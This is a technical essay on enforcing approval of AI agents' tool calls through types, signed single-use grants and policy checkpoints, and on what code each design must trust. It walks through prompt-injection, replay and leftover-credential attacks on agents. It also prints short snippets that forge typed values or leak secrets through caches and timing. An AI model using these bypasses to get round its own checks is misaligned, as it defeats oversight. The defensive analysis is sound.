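A type can provide evidence about code before it runs. Suppose an agent writes a function that summarizes the classified fraud rules but also emails them to an outside address on the first of each month. On any other day, a runtime checkpoint has no email to refuse. On the first, it can refuse the email if it has a suitable policy and can trace where the text came from. Where the program requires a pure function, Scala's capture checking rejects this one on any date because its type includes the email capability.

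Odersky and colleagues use the term "local purity" for the ability to prove that a particular part of a program has no side effects even though the rest does. A runtime can enforce a similar restriction by running that part without access to tools, but it detects an attempted side effect only if that run reaches it.

A system can also keep secrets from an agent without using types. Ma and Schmid store sensitive data outside the agent's runtime and give the agent a reference number and a short summary. In their AgentLeak test, this reduced the share of trials with a leak to 3.23%. Their design needs no special language, but the summaries release some information by design, so somebody has to decide what they may contain.

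Checking a plan in advance can also catch a missing action. Nikolaou and colleagues give the example of a security agent that opens an incident ticket and must eventually resolve it or pass it to another team. If the agent never does either, a checkpoint that examines one call at a time has no call to refuse. Their tool, CaMeLoT, translates the whole plan into a model of its possible steps and searches for a path that breaks the rule. It returns any such path to the planning model, which can repair the plan before any tool runs.

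In a test of seven deliberately unsafe plans, CaMeLoT caught all seven, while a simplified version of CaMeL caught one. The rules chosen for the test are hard to express in CaMeL, so the result shows a difference in what the two systems can check. It doesn't measure how often such plans occur.

A team can also use types inside the central checkpoint. The memory service may start with one function that receives writes and later add others for bulk imports and administrators. If its storage function accepts only an `AdmittedWrite`, a developer who adds a new write function and forgets the evaluation gets a compiler error. The company's other software has to send its writes through the service, because only the service can access the database.

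## How does an approval reach a tool that runs in another process?

A memory service that evaluates every write itself doesn't need an approval from elsewhere. But a company may prefer to have one policy service that holds the rules for memory, payments and email, looks up where the agent's text came from and waits for managers to respond. Each tool then only carries out what the policy service has approved. The approval has to pass from one program to another, and a type can't protect it in transit.

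### Why a type stops at the process boundary

To send an admitted write over a network, the policy service has to serialize it, which means turning it into a sequence of bytes. The result might be this JSON text:

```json
{"key": "refund_policy",
 "value": "Refunds under $20 do not require manager approval.",
 "authority": "finance"}
```

The memory service then deserializes the bytes, which means it builds a value from them. An ordinary deserializer checks only that the fields are present and correctly formatted, so it would accept the same text from an agent that never contacted the policy service. Private fields don't prevent this, because they restrict what code can do and the agent only has to send bytes. Writing both services in Rust with the same definition of `AdmittedWrite` doesn't help either, because the compiler checked the policy service's code but the memory service can't verify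 that the bytes came from that code.

The memory service therefore needs a function that checks evidence of the approval before it creates the value:

```rust
fn redeem(request: &[u8], grant: &[u8]) -> Result<AdmittedWrite, GrantError>;
```

An approval reaches a tool in another process as an execution grant, a short-lived record of one approved action that the tool can verify for itself. If only the code that verifies the grant can create an `AdmittedWrite` in the memory service, the types again protect `persist` from unapproved writes after that check.

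### The life of a grant

Suppose the finance team decides that refunds under $20 need no manager's approval, and asks the agent to record the rule.

1. The agent proposes the write. The policy service converts it to a standard, or canonical, form, as Faramesh does.
2. The policy service evaluates the proposal, finds that the rule came from the finance team and allows it.
3. It computes a hash of the canonical form and puts the hash into a grant.
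4. It signs the grant with a private key. The memory service can check the signature with the matching public key, but can't use that key to sign grants of its own.
5. The agent sends its request to the memory service with the grant attached.
6. The memory service checks the signature, the expiry time, the agent's identity and that the grant is for this tool. It converts the request to canonical form itself and compares the hashes.
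7. In one database transaction, it confirms that the grant is unused, marks it as used and stores the entry.

The grant might look like this:

```text
number:     417
agent:      support-agent
tool:       memory-service, persist
action:     (hash of the canonical request)
policy:     refund rules, version 12
expires:    10:10
signature:  (covers every line above)
```

Suppose an email hijacks the agent after it receives the grant but before it sends the request. The agent changes $20 to $2,000 and attaches the genuine grant. The signature is still valid because the grant hasn't changed. But the hash of the new request doesn't match the hash in the grant, so the memory service refuses the request. If the agent also replaces the hash in the grant, the signature is no longer valid. A tool that checked the signature but not the hash would store the $2,000 rule.

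A replay reuses a grant without changing anything. The memory service stores the $20 rule at 10:02, and the finance team withdraws it at 10:05. At 10:06 the hijacked agent resends the original request and grant to restore the rule. The signature and hash are correct and the grant hasn't expired, so only the record that grant 417 was already used stops the write.

Wu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) point out in *From Intent to Execution Grant* that a unique number in each grant isn't enough to prevent the grant from being reused. If the memory service runs on two servers that keep separate lists of used numbers, the agent can use the grant once on each. The servers need one shared list, and no other request may come between checking it and updating it.

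Payments are harder, because the company's database and its bank can't take part in the same transaction. If the payment service marks the grant as used and crashes before paying, an approved payment may never happen. If it pays first and crashes before marking the grant, it can pay the invoice again with the same grant. Marking the grant first is usually safer, because before anyone issues another grant, a person can check whether the money left.

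Restricted tokens are older than AI agents. Macaroons, a token format from 2014, attach conditions, called caveats, to a credential, and a service accepts the credential only if they are met. Wu and colleagues note that the format doesn't specify how to tie a token to one exact action or how to invalidate it after use.

### AgentCap's seven conditions

Suresh and Gao (2026), in *AGENTCAP*, apply such tokens to tools that agents reach through the Model Context Protocol. A wrapper around the tools submits each proposed call to a policy engine, which issues a signed capability token if it approves. A separate gateway verifies the token before it forwards the call. The engine issues a token only if all of these conditions hold:

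1. The system hasn't sandboxed the agent for suspicious behaviour.
2. The requested tool is in the policy's catalogue.
3. Protected arguments, such as the recipient of a payment, don't come solely from untrusted text.
4. The policy permits the purpose that the agent declares for the call.
5. The agent's trust score is high enough.
6. The agent holds valid tokens for any prerequisites in the same session. For example, it may need permission to read an account balance before it can send money.
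7. The new token wouldn't complete a forbidden combination, such as access to sensitive data together with a way to send it out.

If the policy protects the text of memory entries, the third condition blocks a refund rule that appears only in a customer's email. It admits the same rule if the user's own request contains it. The declared purpose is much weaker evidence because the model supplies it, and a hijacked model can declare whatever purpose the policy accepts.

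The trust score starts at 0.8. Each refusal or anomalous result multiplies it by 0.7, and each normal result closes 1% of the gap between the score and 1. After three anomalies in a row the score is 0.274, and the system sandboxes the agent. The sample banking policy requires a score of at least 0.8 for payments. One refused call lowers the score from 0.8 to 0.56, and the agent then needs 79 normal results before it can pay anyone. An attacker who can't steal money might still plant instructions that provoke refusals and so stop the agent from working.

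AgentCap's token specifies the agent, session, action, resource, purpose, expiry time and maximum number of calls. It doesn't include the arguments or a hash of them. If the agent obtained a token for the $20 rule and the gateway received it with the $2,000 rule, the gateway couldn't detect the change from the token. The design relies on the trusted wrapper to forward exactly the call that the engine checked.

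An agent can delegate a token to another agent in the same session. The new token covers the same action and resource, can't last longer or allow more calls than the original, and permits fewer further delegations. The gateway checks every signature in the chain back to the policy engine.

Suresh and Gao tested AgentCap on AgentDojo's 949 attack trials and on InjecAgent, another prompt-injection benchmark, which has 1,054:

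| Benchmark and model | Successful attacks, undefended | Successful attacks, AgentCap | Tasks completed under attack, undefended | Tasks completed under attack, AgentCap |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 45.63% | 5.09% | 73.61% | 74.88% |
| AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | 33.23% | 0.00% | 75.68% | 75.04% |
| InjecAgent, GPT-4o | 23.24% | 8.63% | 74.10% | 62.24% |
| InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 | 11.95% | 0.00% | 72.96% | 65.37% |

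When there were no attacks, AgentCap lowered the task completion rate by 3.1 to 11.7 percentage points. Issuing a token typically took 67 microseconds and verifying one took 80, so the checks add almost no delay. Each condition was run only once.

Some of the attacks that still worked with GPT-4o were meant only to produce a misleading reply, which no check on tools can stop. Others used tool arguments that the policy didn't protect, or text from a field that the policy hadn't labelled as untrusted. Suresh and Gao describe these as gaps in the policy.

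AgentCap's developers wrote the AgentDojo policies by hand, after reading the descriptions of the tools and the user tasks but before running the tests. A company can't read its users' requests in advance. The handwritten policies also complicate the comparison with Progent, in which a model generates the policy for each task. Under attack, Progent completed 59.64% of tasks and AgentCap completed 74.88%, but some of that difference probably comes from the handwritten rules rather than the tokens.

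### What EBL-Core requires

Wu and colleagues define a conformance profile called EBL-Core, which lists the requirements a system must meet to claim that it controls the release of authority to act. The profile separates the record of a decision from the permission to act on it. An execution release contract records what the system decided and under which conditions. An auditor can use the contract to verify the decision, but nobody can use it to perform an action such as moving money. A grant provides that permission, and the tool "redeems" the grant by checking it and performing the action.

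In the paper's worked example, a treasury department authorizes a transfer to Alice, an approved recipient, of up to 10,000 USDC, a digital currency tied to the dollar. The agent proposes sending 7,500. Every detail, including the recipient, the network and the maximum fee, must be final before the decision. A root policy caps transfers at 10,000. An operational policy, which can add restrictions but can't relax the root policy, lowers the cap to 9,000. The system also needs evidence that Alice is on the approved list, that the account has enough money and that the required people have approved. It classifies the evidence for each requirement as valid, unknown, missing, expired or conflicting, and allows the transfer only if all of it is valid.

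When the agent presents the grant, the tool must verify that the transfer is exactly the approved one and that the grant is still unused. The policy versions, the evidence and the surrounding facts must also not have changed since the decision. If anyone changes the recipient from Alice to Bob, the tool refuses the transfer.

The rule about surrounding facts could invalidate grants unnecessarily. In the example, those facts include the account's balance and a version number for the ledger. A customer's unrelated deposit would change both, so the grant would stop working even though the deposit makes the transfer safer. On a busy account, the agent might need several decisions before one transfer succeeds.

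EBL-Core has four levels of conformance:

| Level | What the system must add |
|---|---|
| 0 | A decision to allow or deny, with a stable reason, and refusal of malformed requests |
| 1 | A verifiable decision about one exact action |
| 2 | A grant for that exact action, which the tool can redeem only once |
| 3 | An independently specified verifier, published tests and evaluation across implementations |

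A system must reach Level 2 to claim that it conforms to the profile for releasing authority. AgentCap's published token probably wouldn't meet Level 2, because it doesn't identify the exact arguments.

The accompanying Python program produced the specified result in 34 tests of decisions and 15 tests of grants and related records. In each of 100 further trials, 32 requests to redeem the same grant ran at once, and exactly one succeeded. The program keeps its grants in memory behind a single lock, so the trials don't cover two servers with separate records or a crash halfway through a payment. Wu and colleagues present the results as evidence that the specification can run, not that a deployment would be secure.

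### When the record doesn't control the action

*Proof-Carrying Agent Actions* (Wang, 2026) also attaches a record to each action, but mainly for approval and audit across different agent platforms. The software checks the action, opens a certificate for it, records the assumptions behind it, waits for approval if necessary, and adds the outcome. A reviewer can later replay the decision and look for differences, such as a policy that has since changed.

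The certificate also records whether the approval could have stopped the action. The value "observe only" means the evidence arrived after the action had run or the agent had abandoned it. A certificate can therefore be complete and accurate for an action that nobody had a chance to refuse. In EBL-Core, a tool that redeems grants won't act until it has a grant.

Wang's title uses "proof" to mean evidence that a reviewer can replay, while *Proof-Carrying Contracts* (2026) uses the word in its mathematical sense. In the latter, the agent must prove that each call preserves the conditions in a contract. A separate component checks the proof, and the call doesn't run without one.

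Wang expanded 24 scenarios into 96 test cases across four kinds of platform. The system chose the intended response (allow the action, simulate it first, ask for approval or block it) in every case, while a set of fixed rules did so in 58.3%. Nobody else can check these figures, because Wang hasn't published the scenarios or the decision thresholds. On average, only 51.6% of the records expected from the platforms were present, since some platforms report on an action only afterwards.

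### Why checking a skill in advance isn't enough

*PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) argues that a company often can't establish in advance that a skill, a package of instructions and code that an agent can load, is safe. If it could, it might not need to check every call. The paper's example is a skill for sending email. Its code always calls `send_email(body)`, and its written instructions tell the model what to put in the body. The instructions in a safe variant supply a fixed template, while those in a leaking variant tell the model to copy a password from its context. A review of the code can't distinguish the two variants because their code and interface are identical.

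To turn this into a theorem, Li and colleagues first define what it means for a skill to be safe at the point where email leaves the system. Let P₀ and P₁ be the probability distributions of the emails that the agent sends when the secret has one value or another. The skill is safe if

d(P₀, P₁) ≤ δ for every context and every pair of secrets,

where d is the largest difference in the probability that the two distributions give to any set of emails, and δ is the tolerated leak. The theorem then makes two assumptions. The review gives a safe and a leaking variant the same verdict, and an attacker can find a context in which the leaking variant exceeds δ. A rule that depends only on the verdict has to treat both variants alike. If it removes the check on outgoing email for the safe one, it also removes it for the leaking one. A rule that never permits a leak must therefore keep the check for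 both.

A review can still reject bad skills. Anyone who reads the two sets of instructions can distinguish a template from a request to copy a password, and the theorem doesn't apply when the reviewer tells the variants apart. The theorem applies to written instructions only if the attacker can phrase the harmful request so that the reviewer misses it. However, passing a review isn't a good enough reason to stop checking a skill's calls.

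### How PACE decides at the last moment

PACE makes its decision immediately before a tool runs, when the actual arguments are available. It freezes the call, records where each argument came from and lists the effects the call would have. It then runs two checks.

The path check builds a graph of how data reached the call. If the graph connects a secret or untrusted text to an unsafe effect, the check looks for the smallest intervention that breaks the connection, which often means blocking the call. It recognizes secrets in certain encodings, but misses them if the agent paraphrases, translates or splits them.

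The authority check compares the call's effects with permissions derived from the user's authenticated request. These permissions cover the operation, resource, arguments, budget and expiry time, and text from the model can't extend them. If the user asked only for a summary of support emails, the agent has no authority to change refund policy, even if it has a memory tool.

The certified version of PACE applies both the path check and the authority check to the final action. Li and colleagues tested a more permissive version. It can restore a call that the path check blocked if the authority check accepts it, and can repair a call without rechecking it. Their proofs therefore don't cover every action in the experiments.

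The evaluation of PACE used eight benchmarks and three models, and compared PACE with other defences on 79 combinations of model and attack type. PACE had the lowest attack success rate in 62 combinations and tied for the lowest in 14. In the other three, a competing defence had a lower rate, but agents using it completed far fewer tasks. On the full benchmarks, PACE reduced utility by at most 2.92 percentage points compared with an undefended agent.

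The ranking depends partly on how well Li and colleagues set up the competing systems. In their AgentDojo tests with gpt-5.6-luna, the most effective type of attack succeeded against CaMeL 36.09% of the time, although other groups found almost no successful attacks against it. With the same model, 30.77% of attacks still succeeded against PACE in the harder version of InjecAgent, down from 50.5% without a defence.

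A separate experiment on 1,167 cases, with the model Qwen-3.8-27B, switched parts of PACE on and off:

| Version | Successful attacks, AgentDojo | Tasks completed, AgentDojo | Successful attacks, AgentDyn | Tasks completed, AgentDyn |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No checks | 37.4% | 76.8% | 25.0% | 66.7% |
| Path check only | 0.0% | 13.6% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Authority check only | 0.0% | 64.6% | 1.7% | 36.7% |
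| Full system | 0.0% | 67.2% | 0.0% | 33.3% |

The path check alone stopped attacks mainly because it blocked nearly all work. The authority check alone was almost as secure and far more useful. The full system lost little utility on the full benchmarks, but it halved the number of completed tasks on the selection of cases from AgentDyn, a benchmark of changing environments.

Li and colleagues also searched for attacks designed to beat PACE. On 30 AgentDojo cases, the search succeeded 21 times against an undefended agent and never against PACE. With so few cases, the true success rate against PACE could still be as high as 11.4% (95% confidence).

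These experiments test the decision about each call but not how that decision reaches another process. Li and colleagues specify single-use tokens and crash recovery for larger deployments, but the software they tested included neither.

### When the agent also has a password

Suppose the company introduces grants for memory writes but keeps the old database password active so that existing scripts continue to work. A write now succeeds under either of two conditions:

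```text
valid grant OR correct password
```

If the agent's process can read the password, a hijacked agent can connect to the database and store the $2,000 rule without forging a signature or replaying a grant. The memory service never receives a request it could refuse.

Wu and colleagues state that EBL-Core can't prevent an agent from using a credential it obtained elsewhere. Suresh and Gao assume that attackers can't get around AgentCap's tool interface, and Li and colleagues likewise assume complete mediation. The low attack rates in their experiments don't apply to a deployment that leaves another route to the tools open.

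These standing credentials are easy to overlook. A developer may have left a payment service's key in an environment variable, or a command-line program may have saved an earlier login. If the agent controls a browser, the browser may still be signed in to the company's email. An agent with a shell tool could find and use any of these.

As with the central memory service, only the component that verifies grants should hold the tool's credential. The agent's process should also have no access to the key that signs grants. The agent can keep a credential that only identifies it, provided that the verifying component requires a grant as well:

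```text
agent's identity AND valid grant
```

Many outside services accept only their own keys, not grants. For these, the company can run a small intermediary that holds the key, verifies each grant and then calls the service.

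## What code must still be trusted?

The intermediary that holds a payment service's key and verifies grants is a program too. If it compares the wrong hash, a hijacked agent can change an approved payment without forging anything. Every admission design depends on such components, which together make up its trusted computing base. A component is "trusted" if the guarantee depends on it, whether or not anyone has good reason to rely on it.

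The table leaves out the operating system, the hardware and the people who administer the machines, because all six designs depend on them.

| Design | Trusted part | What a failure would allow |
|---|---|---|
| Rust admission module | The module that creates admitted writes | Any write could count as admitted |
| Rust admission module | The compiler, and all `unsafe` and foreign code in the program | Code could forge or alter an admitted write |
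| Rust admission module | Storage passwords, and every library in the same process | Code could write to storage without an admitted write |
| Symbiont | The policy gate | The loop could run in the right order and still approve forbidden actions |
| Symbiont | The executor | Tools could run unapproved actions, or change approved ones |
| Symbiont | Policy files, keys and identity records | The gate could apply the wrong rule, or the right rule to the wrong agent |
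| TACIT | The Scala compiler, with capture checking and safe mode | A function with side effects could pass as pure |
| TACIT | The capability library and `@assumeSafe` modules | Agent code could read secrets, or reach files and hosts outside its scope |
| TACIT | The runtime that executes the code | Code could escape its limits after passing the type check |
| TACIT | The local model | Secrets could leave through the model's logs, or reappear in a later reply |
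| ELBA | The Haskell compiler and its safe subset | A program with a pure type could write files |
| ELBA | The developer's effect library | The agent could run any operation, or forge trusted values |
| ELBA | LIO and the labels on data | Untrusted text could influence a restricted action |
| Central checkpoint | The policy engine and tool adapters | A forbidden action could run, or an allowed request could become a different action |
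| Central checkpoint | Passwords and network rules | Programs could reach the resource without the checkpoint |
| Central checkpoint | The records and labels that rules use | The engine could apply a correct rule to false facts |
| Signed grants | The policy service and its signing key | Whoever controls either could approve any action |
| Signed grants | The code that verifies grants | A tool could accept a changed or expired request |
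| Signed grants | The shared record of used grants | An attacker could repeat an approved action |

The table does not include the model that proposes actions or the emails and web pages it reads. A system that relies on the model to avoid unsafe actions adds billions of parameters that nobody can review to its trusted base.

### Ways around a type system

Most languages let programmers switch off some of the compiler's checks, as Rust does with `unsafe`. Suppose the `Authority` in an admitted write is a plain list of options that fits in one byte. Any module could then define a look-alike struct and relabel it:

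```rust
struct Fake { key: String, value: String, authority: u8 }

let forged: custody::AdmittedWrite = unsafe { std::mem::transmute(fake) };
persist(forged);
```

`transmute` reinterprets the bytes of one type as another, even if the fields are private. Rust doesn't promise to lay out two structs with the same fields identically, but it probably will. A team can search its code for the `unsafe` keyword, and the line `#![forbid(unsafe_code)]` makes the compiler reject `unsafe` blocks throughout a crate, but not in the crates it imports.

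Foreign functions cause a similar problem. If the company keeps its agent's memory in SQLite, the Rust program calls a C library that shares its address space and permissions. A bug in the library could alter a write after `evaluate` has approved it. Such bugs can also expose data. Heartbleed, a 2014 flaw in the encryption library OpenSSL, let attackers read the memory of web servers, and a similar flaw in the policy service could reveal the key that signs grants. Using a Rust library for the signatures only partly reduces this risk, because fast cryptography in Rust still relies largely on `unsafe` code and assembly.

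An imported crate can also supply a procedural macro, a program that generates code during compilation. If a developer applies one to `AdmittedWrite`, the generated code goes inside the `custody` module, where it can create admitted writes. Anyone reviewing the module must therefore also review the macros it uses.

Scala runs on the Java virtual machine, where reflection can often read and change private fields. Safe mode bans reflection and unchecked casts in the agent's snippets, but not in the rest of the process. Odersky and colleagues let the objects that the agent receives as capabilities come from any module. These objects' methods may contain code that safe mode would reject, so whoever designs the interface has to vouch for that code.

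Haskell's best-known escape hatch is `unsafePerformIO`, which runs an operation with side effects and gives the result a pure type:

```haskell
answer :: Int
answer = unsafePerformIO (writeFile "memory/refund_policy" rule >> return 120)
```

`answer` has the type `Int`, so the public calculator from the ELBA example would accept it, but computing the number would also store the rule. Zhou and colleagues respond that Safe Haskell, a subset of the language selected by a compiler flag, excludes such functions. The guarantee depends on that flag being set whenever ELBA compiles an agent's program. Safe Haskell also lets a library's author mark it as trustworthy even though it uses unsafe features internally, so those libraries must also be trusted.

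### Soundness bugs in compilers

A type system is unsound if a program can compile and still break the rules that its types express. The Haskell and Rust compilers have both had bugs that allowed this.

GHC, the main Haskell compiler, can copy the operations of an existing type to a new type with the same representation. In 2007 a bug report showed that this feature, combined with another extension, let a program convert a value to an unrelated type without calling any unsafe function. GHC's developers fixed the bug in 2014 with stricter rules about which types are interchangeable. Safe Haskell banned the feature while the bug remained.

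In 2015, Rust's developers received a report of a flaw in how the compiler handles lifetimes, the periods during which references stay valid. Code without `unsafe` blocks can use the flaw to treat a short-lived reference as permanent, and then build its own version of `transmute`. The report was still open ten years later because a full fix depends on redesigning part of the type checker.

Neither bug is likely to put a refund rule into memory by accident. The lifetime exploit needs an oddly constructed function that no import routine would contain. But an attacker can write such a function on purpose. Untrusted Rust extensions that appeared safe could corrupt the kernel of RedLeaf, an experimental operating system that relies on Rust for isolation, and could leak private data from Sesame, a system for protecting such data.

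TACIT and ELBA are closer to those systems than to the company's own Rust program, because they compile code that an attacker may have influenced. Both also return the compiler's errors to the agent, which a hijacked agent could use to search for a compiler bug. The attacks in the TACIT experiments didn't include such a search, so the perfect security score provides little evidence about that risk.

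### Small libraries with a lot of authority

TACIT's reusable library is about 1,000 lines of Scala. It wraps secrets, opens files, starts commands and contacts hosts, so one missing check in it could defeat the compiler's protections. Each application also needs a facade, a set of typed functions that represent its tools. The facades for the airline and retail tests are a few hundred lines each. Odersky and colleagues suggest that agents could help write facades, because people review them before the agent runs. Reviewers have to look for missing capabilities in particular, because if a function sends email but its signature doesn't mention a capability, the compiler will treat it as pure.

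Modules marked `@assumeSafe` need the same care. Odersky and colleagues give the example of a cache that stores earlier results in a mutable map, which is harmless as long as nobody can observe the map. A small addition can make it observable:

```scala
@assumeSafe object Lengths:
  private val cache = mutable.Map[String, Int]()
  def length(s: String): Int = cache.getOrElseUpdate(s, s.length)
  def seen(s: String): Boolean = cache.contains(s)
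```

With `length` alone, the result depends only on the argument. The function `seen`, which a developer might add for debugging, reveals what other code has looked up. Suppose a classified file contains a four-digit PIN. The agent calls `pin.map(Lengths.length)`, which the compiler accepts as pure, and then calls `Lengths.seen` on each of the 10,000 possible PINs until a call returns true. The agent learns the PIN without unwrapping the secret, and the compiler reports no error because the annotation makes it skip these checks.

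The local model's type also depends on an assumption that the compiler can't check. TACIT has one version of `chat` for classified text and another for ordinary text, which returns an ordinary reply. Both count as pure. Odersky and colleagues note that this requires the model's service to be stateless, meaning it doesn't keep one request as context for the next. If an administrator switched on conversation history, the agent could send the fraud rules through the classified version, then ask the ordinary version to repeat the previous document and receive it as a plain string.

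A hostile instruction inside a classified document can also mislead the local model. The reply stays classified, so the attacker can't use it to send the document to the cloud model, but the manager who asked for a summary may get a false one.

In ELBA, the most security-sensitive line of code is often an export list. The file library defines its effect type, `RIO`, as a wrapper around Haskell's unrestricted `IO` and hides the constructor. If a developer exported the constructor, an agent could wrap any `IO` operation in it, and the program would still have the permitted type. Developers could make the same mistake in each new effect library.

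### Symbiont's assumptions

*Typestate-Enforced Agent Loops* guarantees the order of phases only under five explicit assumptions. Some concern `unsafe` code and foreign functions, and these hold only if the developers control what enters the program through its dependencies. Other parts of the system must ensure that the policy is correct and the tools are faithful. The preprint concludes that its design "relocates the security surface rather than eliminating it".

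In the published source code of Symbi 1.14.3, the calling program supplies four components, which don't all need the same trust for the guarantee to hold. The component that contacts the model can only produce proposals, which still go through the gate. The one that trims the conversation changes what the model reads. A faulty gate, however, can approve anything, and a faulty executor can run something other than what the gate approved. All four share a process, so a hostile one can also open files or network connections directly.

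Wanger (2026), in *Open Agent Trust Stack (OATS)*, the specification that Symbiont implements, sorts the components into three groups:

| Trust | Components |
|---|---|
| Full | The runtime, including its loop, policy engine, tool executor, identity checks and audit log; cryptography and key management; the stored policies and the process for writing them; the operating system, network and hardware; the compiler and type system |
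| Partial | The tools' own code; the people who approve actions; tool descriptions with a verified signature |
| None | The model and its output; the surrounding agent software; prompts, documents and tool results; the agent's memory; tool descriptions from unverified publishers |

The specification requires that the model be unable to influence the gate's evaluation. Symbi's interface passes the gate the loop's entire state, including the conversation, so whether the model can influence the gate depends on which parts of that state the gate reads. A Cedar rule that compares only the agent's identity and the tool's name is unaffected by the conversation. But a developer could write a gate that searches the conversation for signs that a manager agreed, and a hijacked model could produce those signs.

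The agent's surrounding software is untrusted, but the phase guarantee covers only code that stays inside the loop. Wanger relies on sandboxes and network isolation for code that bypasses the loop.

### Tools, keys and borrowed facts

The tool that carries out an admitted action must still be trusted. If `persist` has a bug that stores entries under the wrong key, a correctly approved note about office hours could overwrite the refund policy. Wanger notes that a runtime can constrain how an agent calls a tool but can't prevent bugs in the tool. Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that for external commands in TACIT, the compiler's guarantee is only as strong as the list of permitted commands.

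Policy engines also depend on facts that other components supply. Symbiont's documentation gives this Cedar rule:

```cedar
forbid(action == Action::"tool_call") when { !resource.verified }
```

The rule blocks any tool that hasn't passed SchemaPin, a component that checks the signature on a tool's description. If SchemaPin wrongly marks a hostile tool as verified, Cedar won't block the call, even though it evaluates the rule correctly. OATS also lists trust on first use among its protections for tools, which means that software stores the key it sees at first contact and rejects a different one later. This catches a later change to a publisher's key, but an attacker who controls the first contact can supply the key that gets stored.

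The same dependence affects refund rules, because `witness` relies on the retrieval component to record where each document came from. If that component files a customer's email attachment under "company handbook", every later stage will work as designed but treat the customer's sentence as company policy.

Leaking a key can do more harm than a large bug. Symbiont's quick start creates a master key and writes it to `.env` in the project directory. An agent with a tool for reading project files might be able to read the key unless its policy or sandbox prevents this. The company can keep the key for signed grants in a separate hardware device that signs data without revealing the key. An attacker who hijacked the policy service could still use the device to sign bad grants, but couldn't copy the key and keep using it after losing control of the service.

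The record of used grants can lose entries during recovery. Suppose the memory service crashes at 10:06 and an administrator restores the record from a copy made at 10:00. Grant 417, which the agent used at 10:02, now looks unused, so the service would accept it again until it expires at 10:10. The service can avoid this by refusing every grant issued before the restart. A server whose clock is an hour behind causes a similar problem, because it will accept grants for an hour after they expire.

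An agent framework must be trusted if a design relies on it to pause or cancel work. Khan (2026), in *Stop Means Stop*, tested six widely used open-source frameworks and found that none reliably prevented actions while a run was paused, cancelled or timed out. Five could pause an action for approval before it ran, but in all five the pause stopped only one branch of the agent's work. An action in a parallel branch could still take effect, so an email may already have been sent by the time a manager rejects the run. *Stop Means Stop* also verifies properties of a gate outside the framework, but it does so on a model of the gate's core and assumes that every action passes through the gate.

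Symbiont's loop avoids one form of this problem by getting the gate's decision on every action in a batch before running any of them. However, denying one action doesn't cancel the approved ones. If the agent proposes a refund and an email confirming it, the gate could deny the refund and let the email go out.

### Leaks through time

TACIT's guarantee excludes side channels, which reveal information through something other than a program's ordinary output. Odersky and colleagues give the example of a function inside `map` that takes longer for some secrets than for others. With helper functions `bit`, which picks out one bit of the text, and `slow`, which computes for about two seconds, the leak fits on one line:

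```scala
key.map(text => if bit(text, 0) then slow(2) else 0)
```

Both helpers are pure, so the compiler accepts the function. The result stays wrapped, but the agent's software can measure how long the call took, and a two-second delay means the first bit is 1. Repeating this for each bit would reveal a 128-bit key in 128 calls, with delays totaling at most 256 seconds.

If the function loops forever when the bit is 1, the timeout also reveals the bit. The server could hide both the running time and the timeout by returning every result after the same fixed delay, but then quick computations would take as long as slow ones. Limiting the number of calls avoids this delay. If an observer can distinguish only two outcomes per call, ten calls reveal at most ten bits, which is too little to recover a key but enough to learn whether a customer is on a fraud list.

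Timing side channels are a much smaller problem for the refund rule than for the fraud rules. To store a false policy, an attacker has to get a write through the admission step, and a delay can't do that. Side channels threaten confidentiality, so they matter mainly in designs that give agents secrets to process.

### What has been proved

RustBelt, a 2018 project by Ralf Jung and colleagues, gave a machine-checked proof that well-typed programs in a core language modelled on Rust don't corrupt memory or access it in conflicting ways from several threads. For each library that uses `unsafe` code internally, it stated the condition that code must meet for the library's public interface to be safe, then proved that several important libraries meet it. This work uncovered an error in Rust's standard library that allowed unsafe sharing through one of its locks, which Rust's developers fixed.

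RustBelt's proof leaves out several features of real Rust and doesn't cover the compiler itself. The lifetime flaw from 2015 is in the real type checker, so it doesn't contradict the theorem. The proof also doesn't establish that `evaluate` always runs before `persist`. A reviewer still has to check the premises about `custody` and the routes to storage.

The type system underlying TACIT's capture checking has machine-checked soundness proofs, but TACIT's security also depends on the rules that safe mode adds. Odersky and colleagues state that a further semantic soundness argument is needed to show that safe mode provides its intended guarantees. Such an argument would have to define what it means for code to hold no capabilities, then prove that every program in safe mode respects that definition. It would also give developers of `@assumeSafe` modules an exact condition to meet. They currently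 have to judge for themselves whether a hidden effect is observable, as in the cache example.

ELBA relies on earlier proofs about LIO. The 2011 paper that introduced LIO proves noninterference for a small language that models the library. The proof doesn't rule out leaks through whether a program finishes. Zhou and colleagues say that ELBA inherits this guarantee.

The library inherits the model's guarantees only as far as it matches the model. In 2013 Pablo Buiras and Alejandro Russo showed that lazy evaluation could leak secrets from a multithreaded version of LIO. Haskell computes a value when a program first needs it and then keeps the result. A thread that handles secrets can therefore speed up a later computation by using a shared value first, and other threads can detect the difference in timing. A small formal model can easily omit such details of the runtime.

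Cedar's developers maintain a mathematical model of the policy language in Lean and compare the production engine with it on large numbers of random inputs. This comparison increases confidence that Cedar evaluates rules correctly, including the one about `verified`, but it does not cover SchemaPin.

None of these proofs covers a complete agent system, from the policy to the tool. A company that combined Rust, Cedar and signed grants would have evidence about some of the parts but would still have to check the code that connects them.

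### Does the trusted base shrink or move?

The argument that typed admission shrinks the trusted base is clearest for the company's own code. If callers have to invoke the guardrail themselves, all 40 places that write to memory are part of the trusted base. If each place has 50 relevant lines, reviewers have to get 2,000 lines right, and every new caller adds 50 more. A typed admission module might have 150 lines, and new callers don't add to the trusted code. These sizes are only illustrative, but the difference in growth doesn't depend on them.

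The objection is that the 150 lines work only because of a compiler with hundreds of thousands. A compiler that large would fail the Anderson panel's requirement that a reference monitor be completely analyzable. The module also shares its process with every imported crate. Counting only the module therefore covers the code that is easy to review and leaves out the rest of what must be trusted.

However, the guardrail also depended on a compiler, which could break it by translating the `if` statement wrongly, and a hostile crate could write to storage under either design. A company that already uses Rust therefore has to trust only one new thing when it adopts typed admission, the soundness of the type system. A hurried developer's mistakes rarely trigger soundness bugs, so the trusted base for preventing those mistakes does get smaller in practice.

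Whether TACIT justifies the extra code that must be trusted depends on what the agent would otherwise use. An agent limited to JSON tool calls submits data, which the trusted software only has to parse and check. Replacing those calls with TACIT lets an attacker submit programs, and adds a compiler, a virtual machine and a capability library to the trusted code. That is probably not worthwhile for an agent that needs only five simple tools. But an agent that would otherwise run Python or shell commands already executes arbitrary programs, so TACIT's restrictions are a clear improvement.

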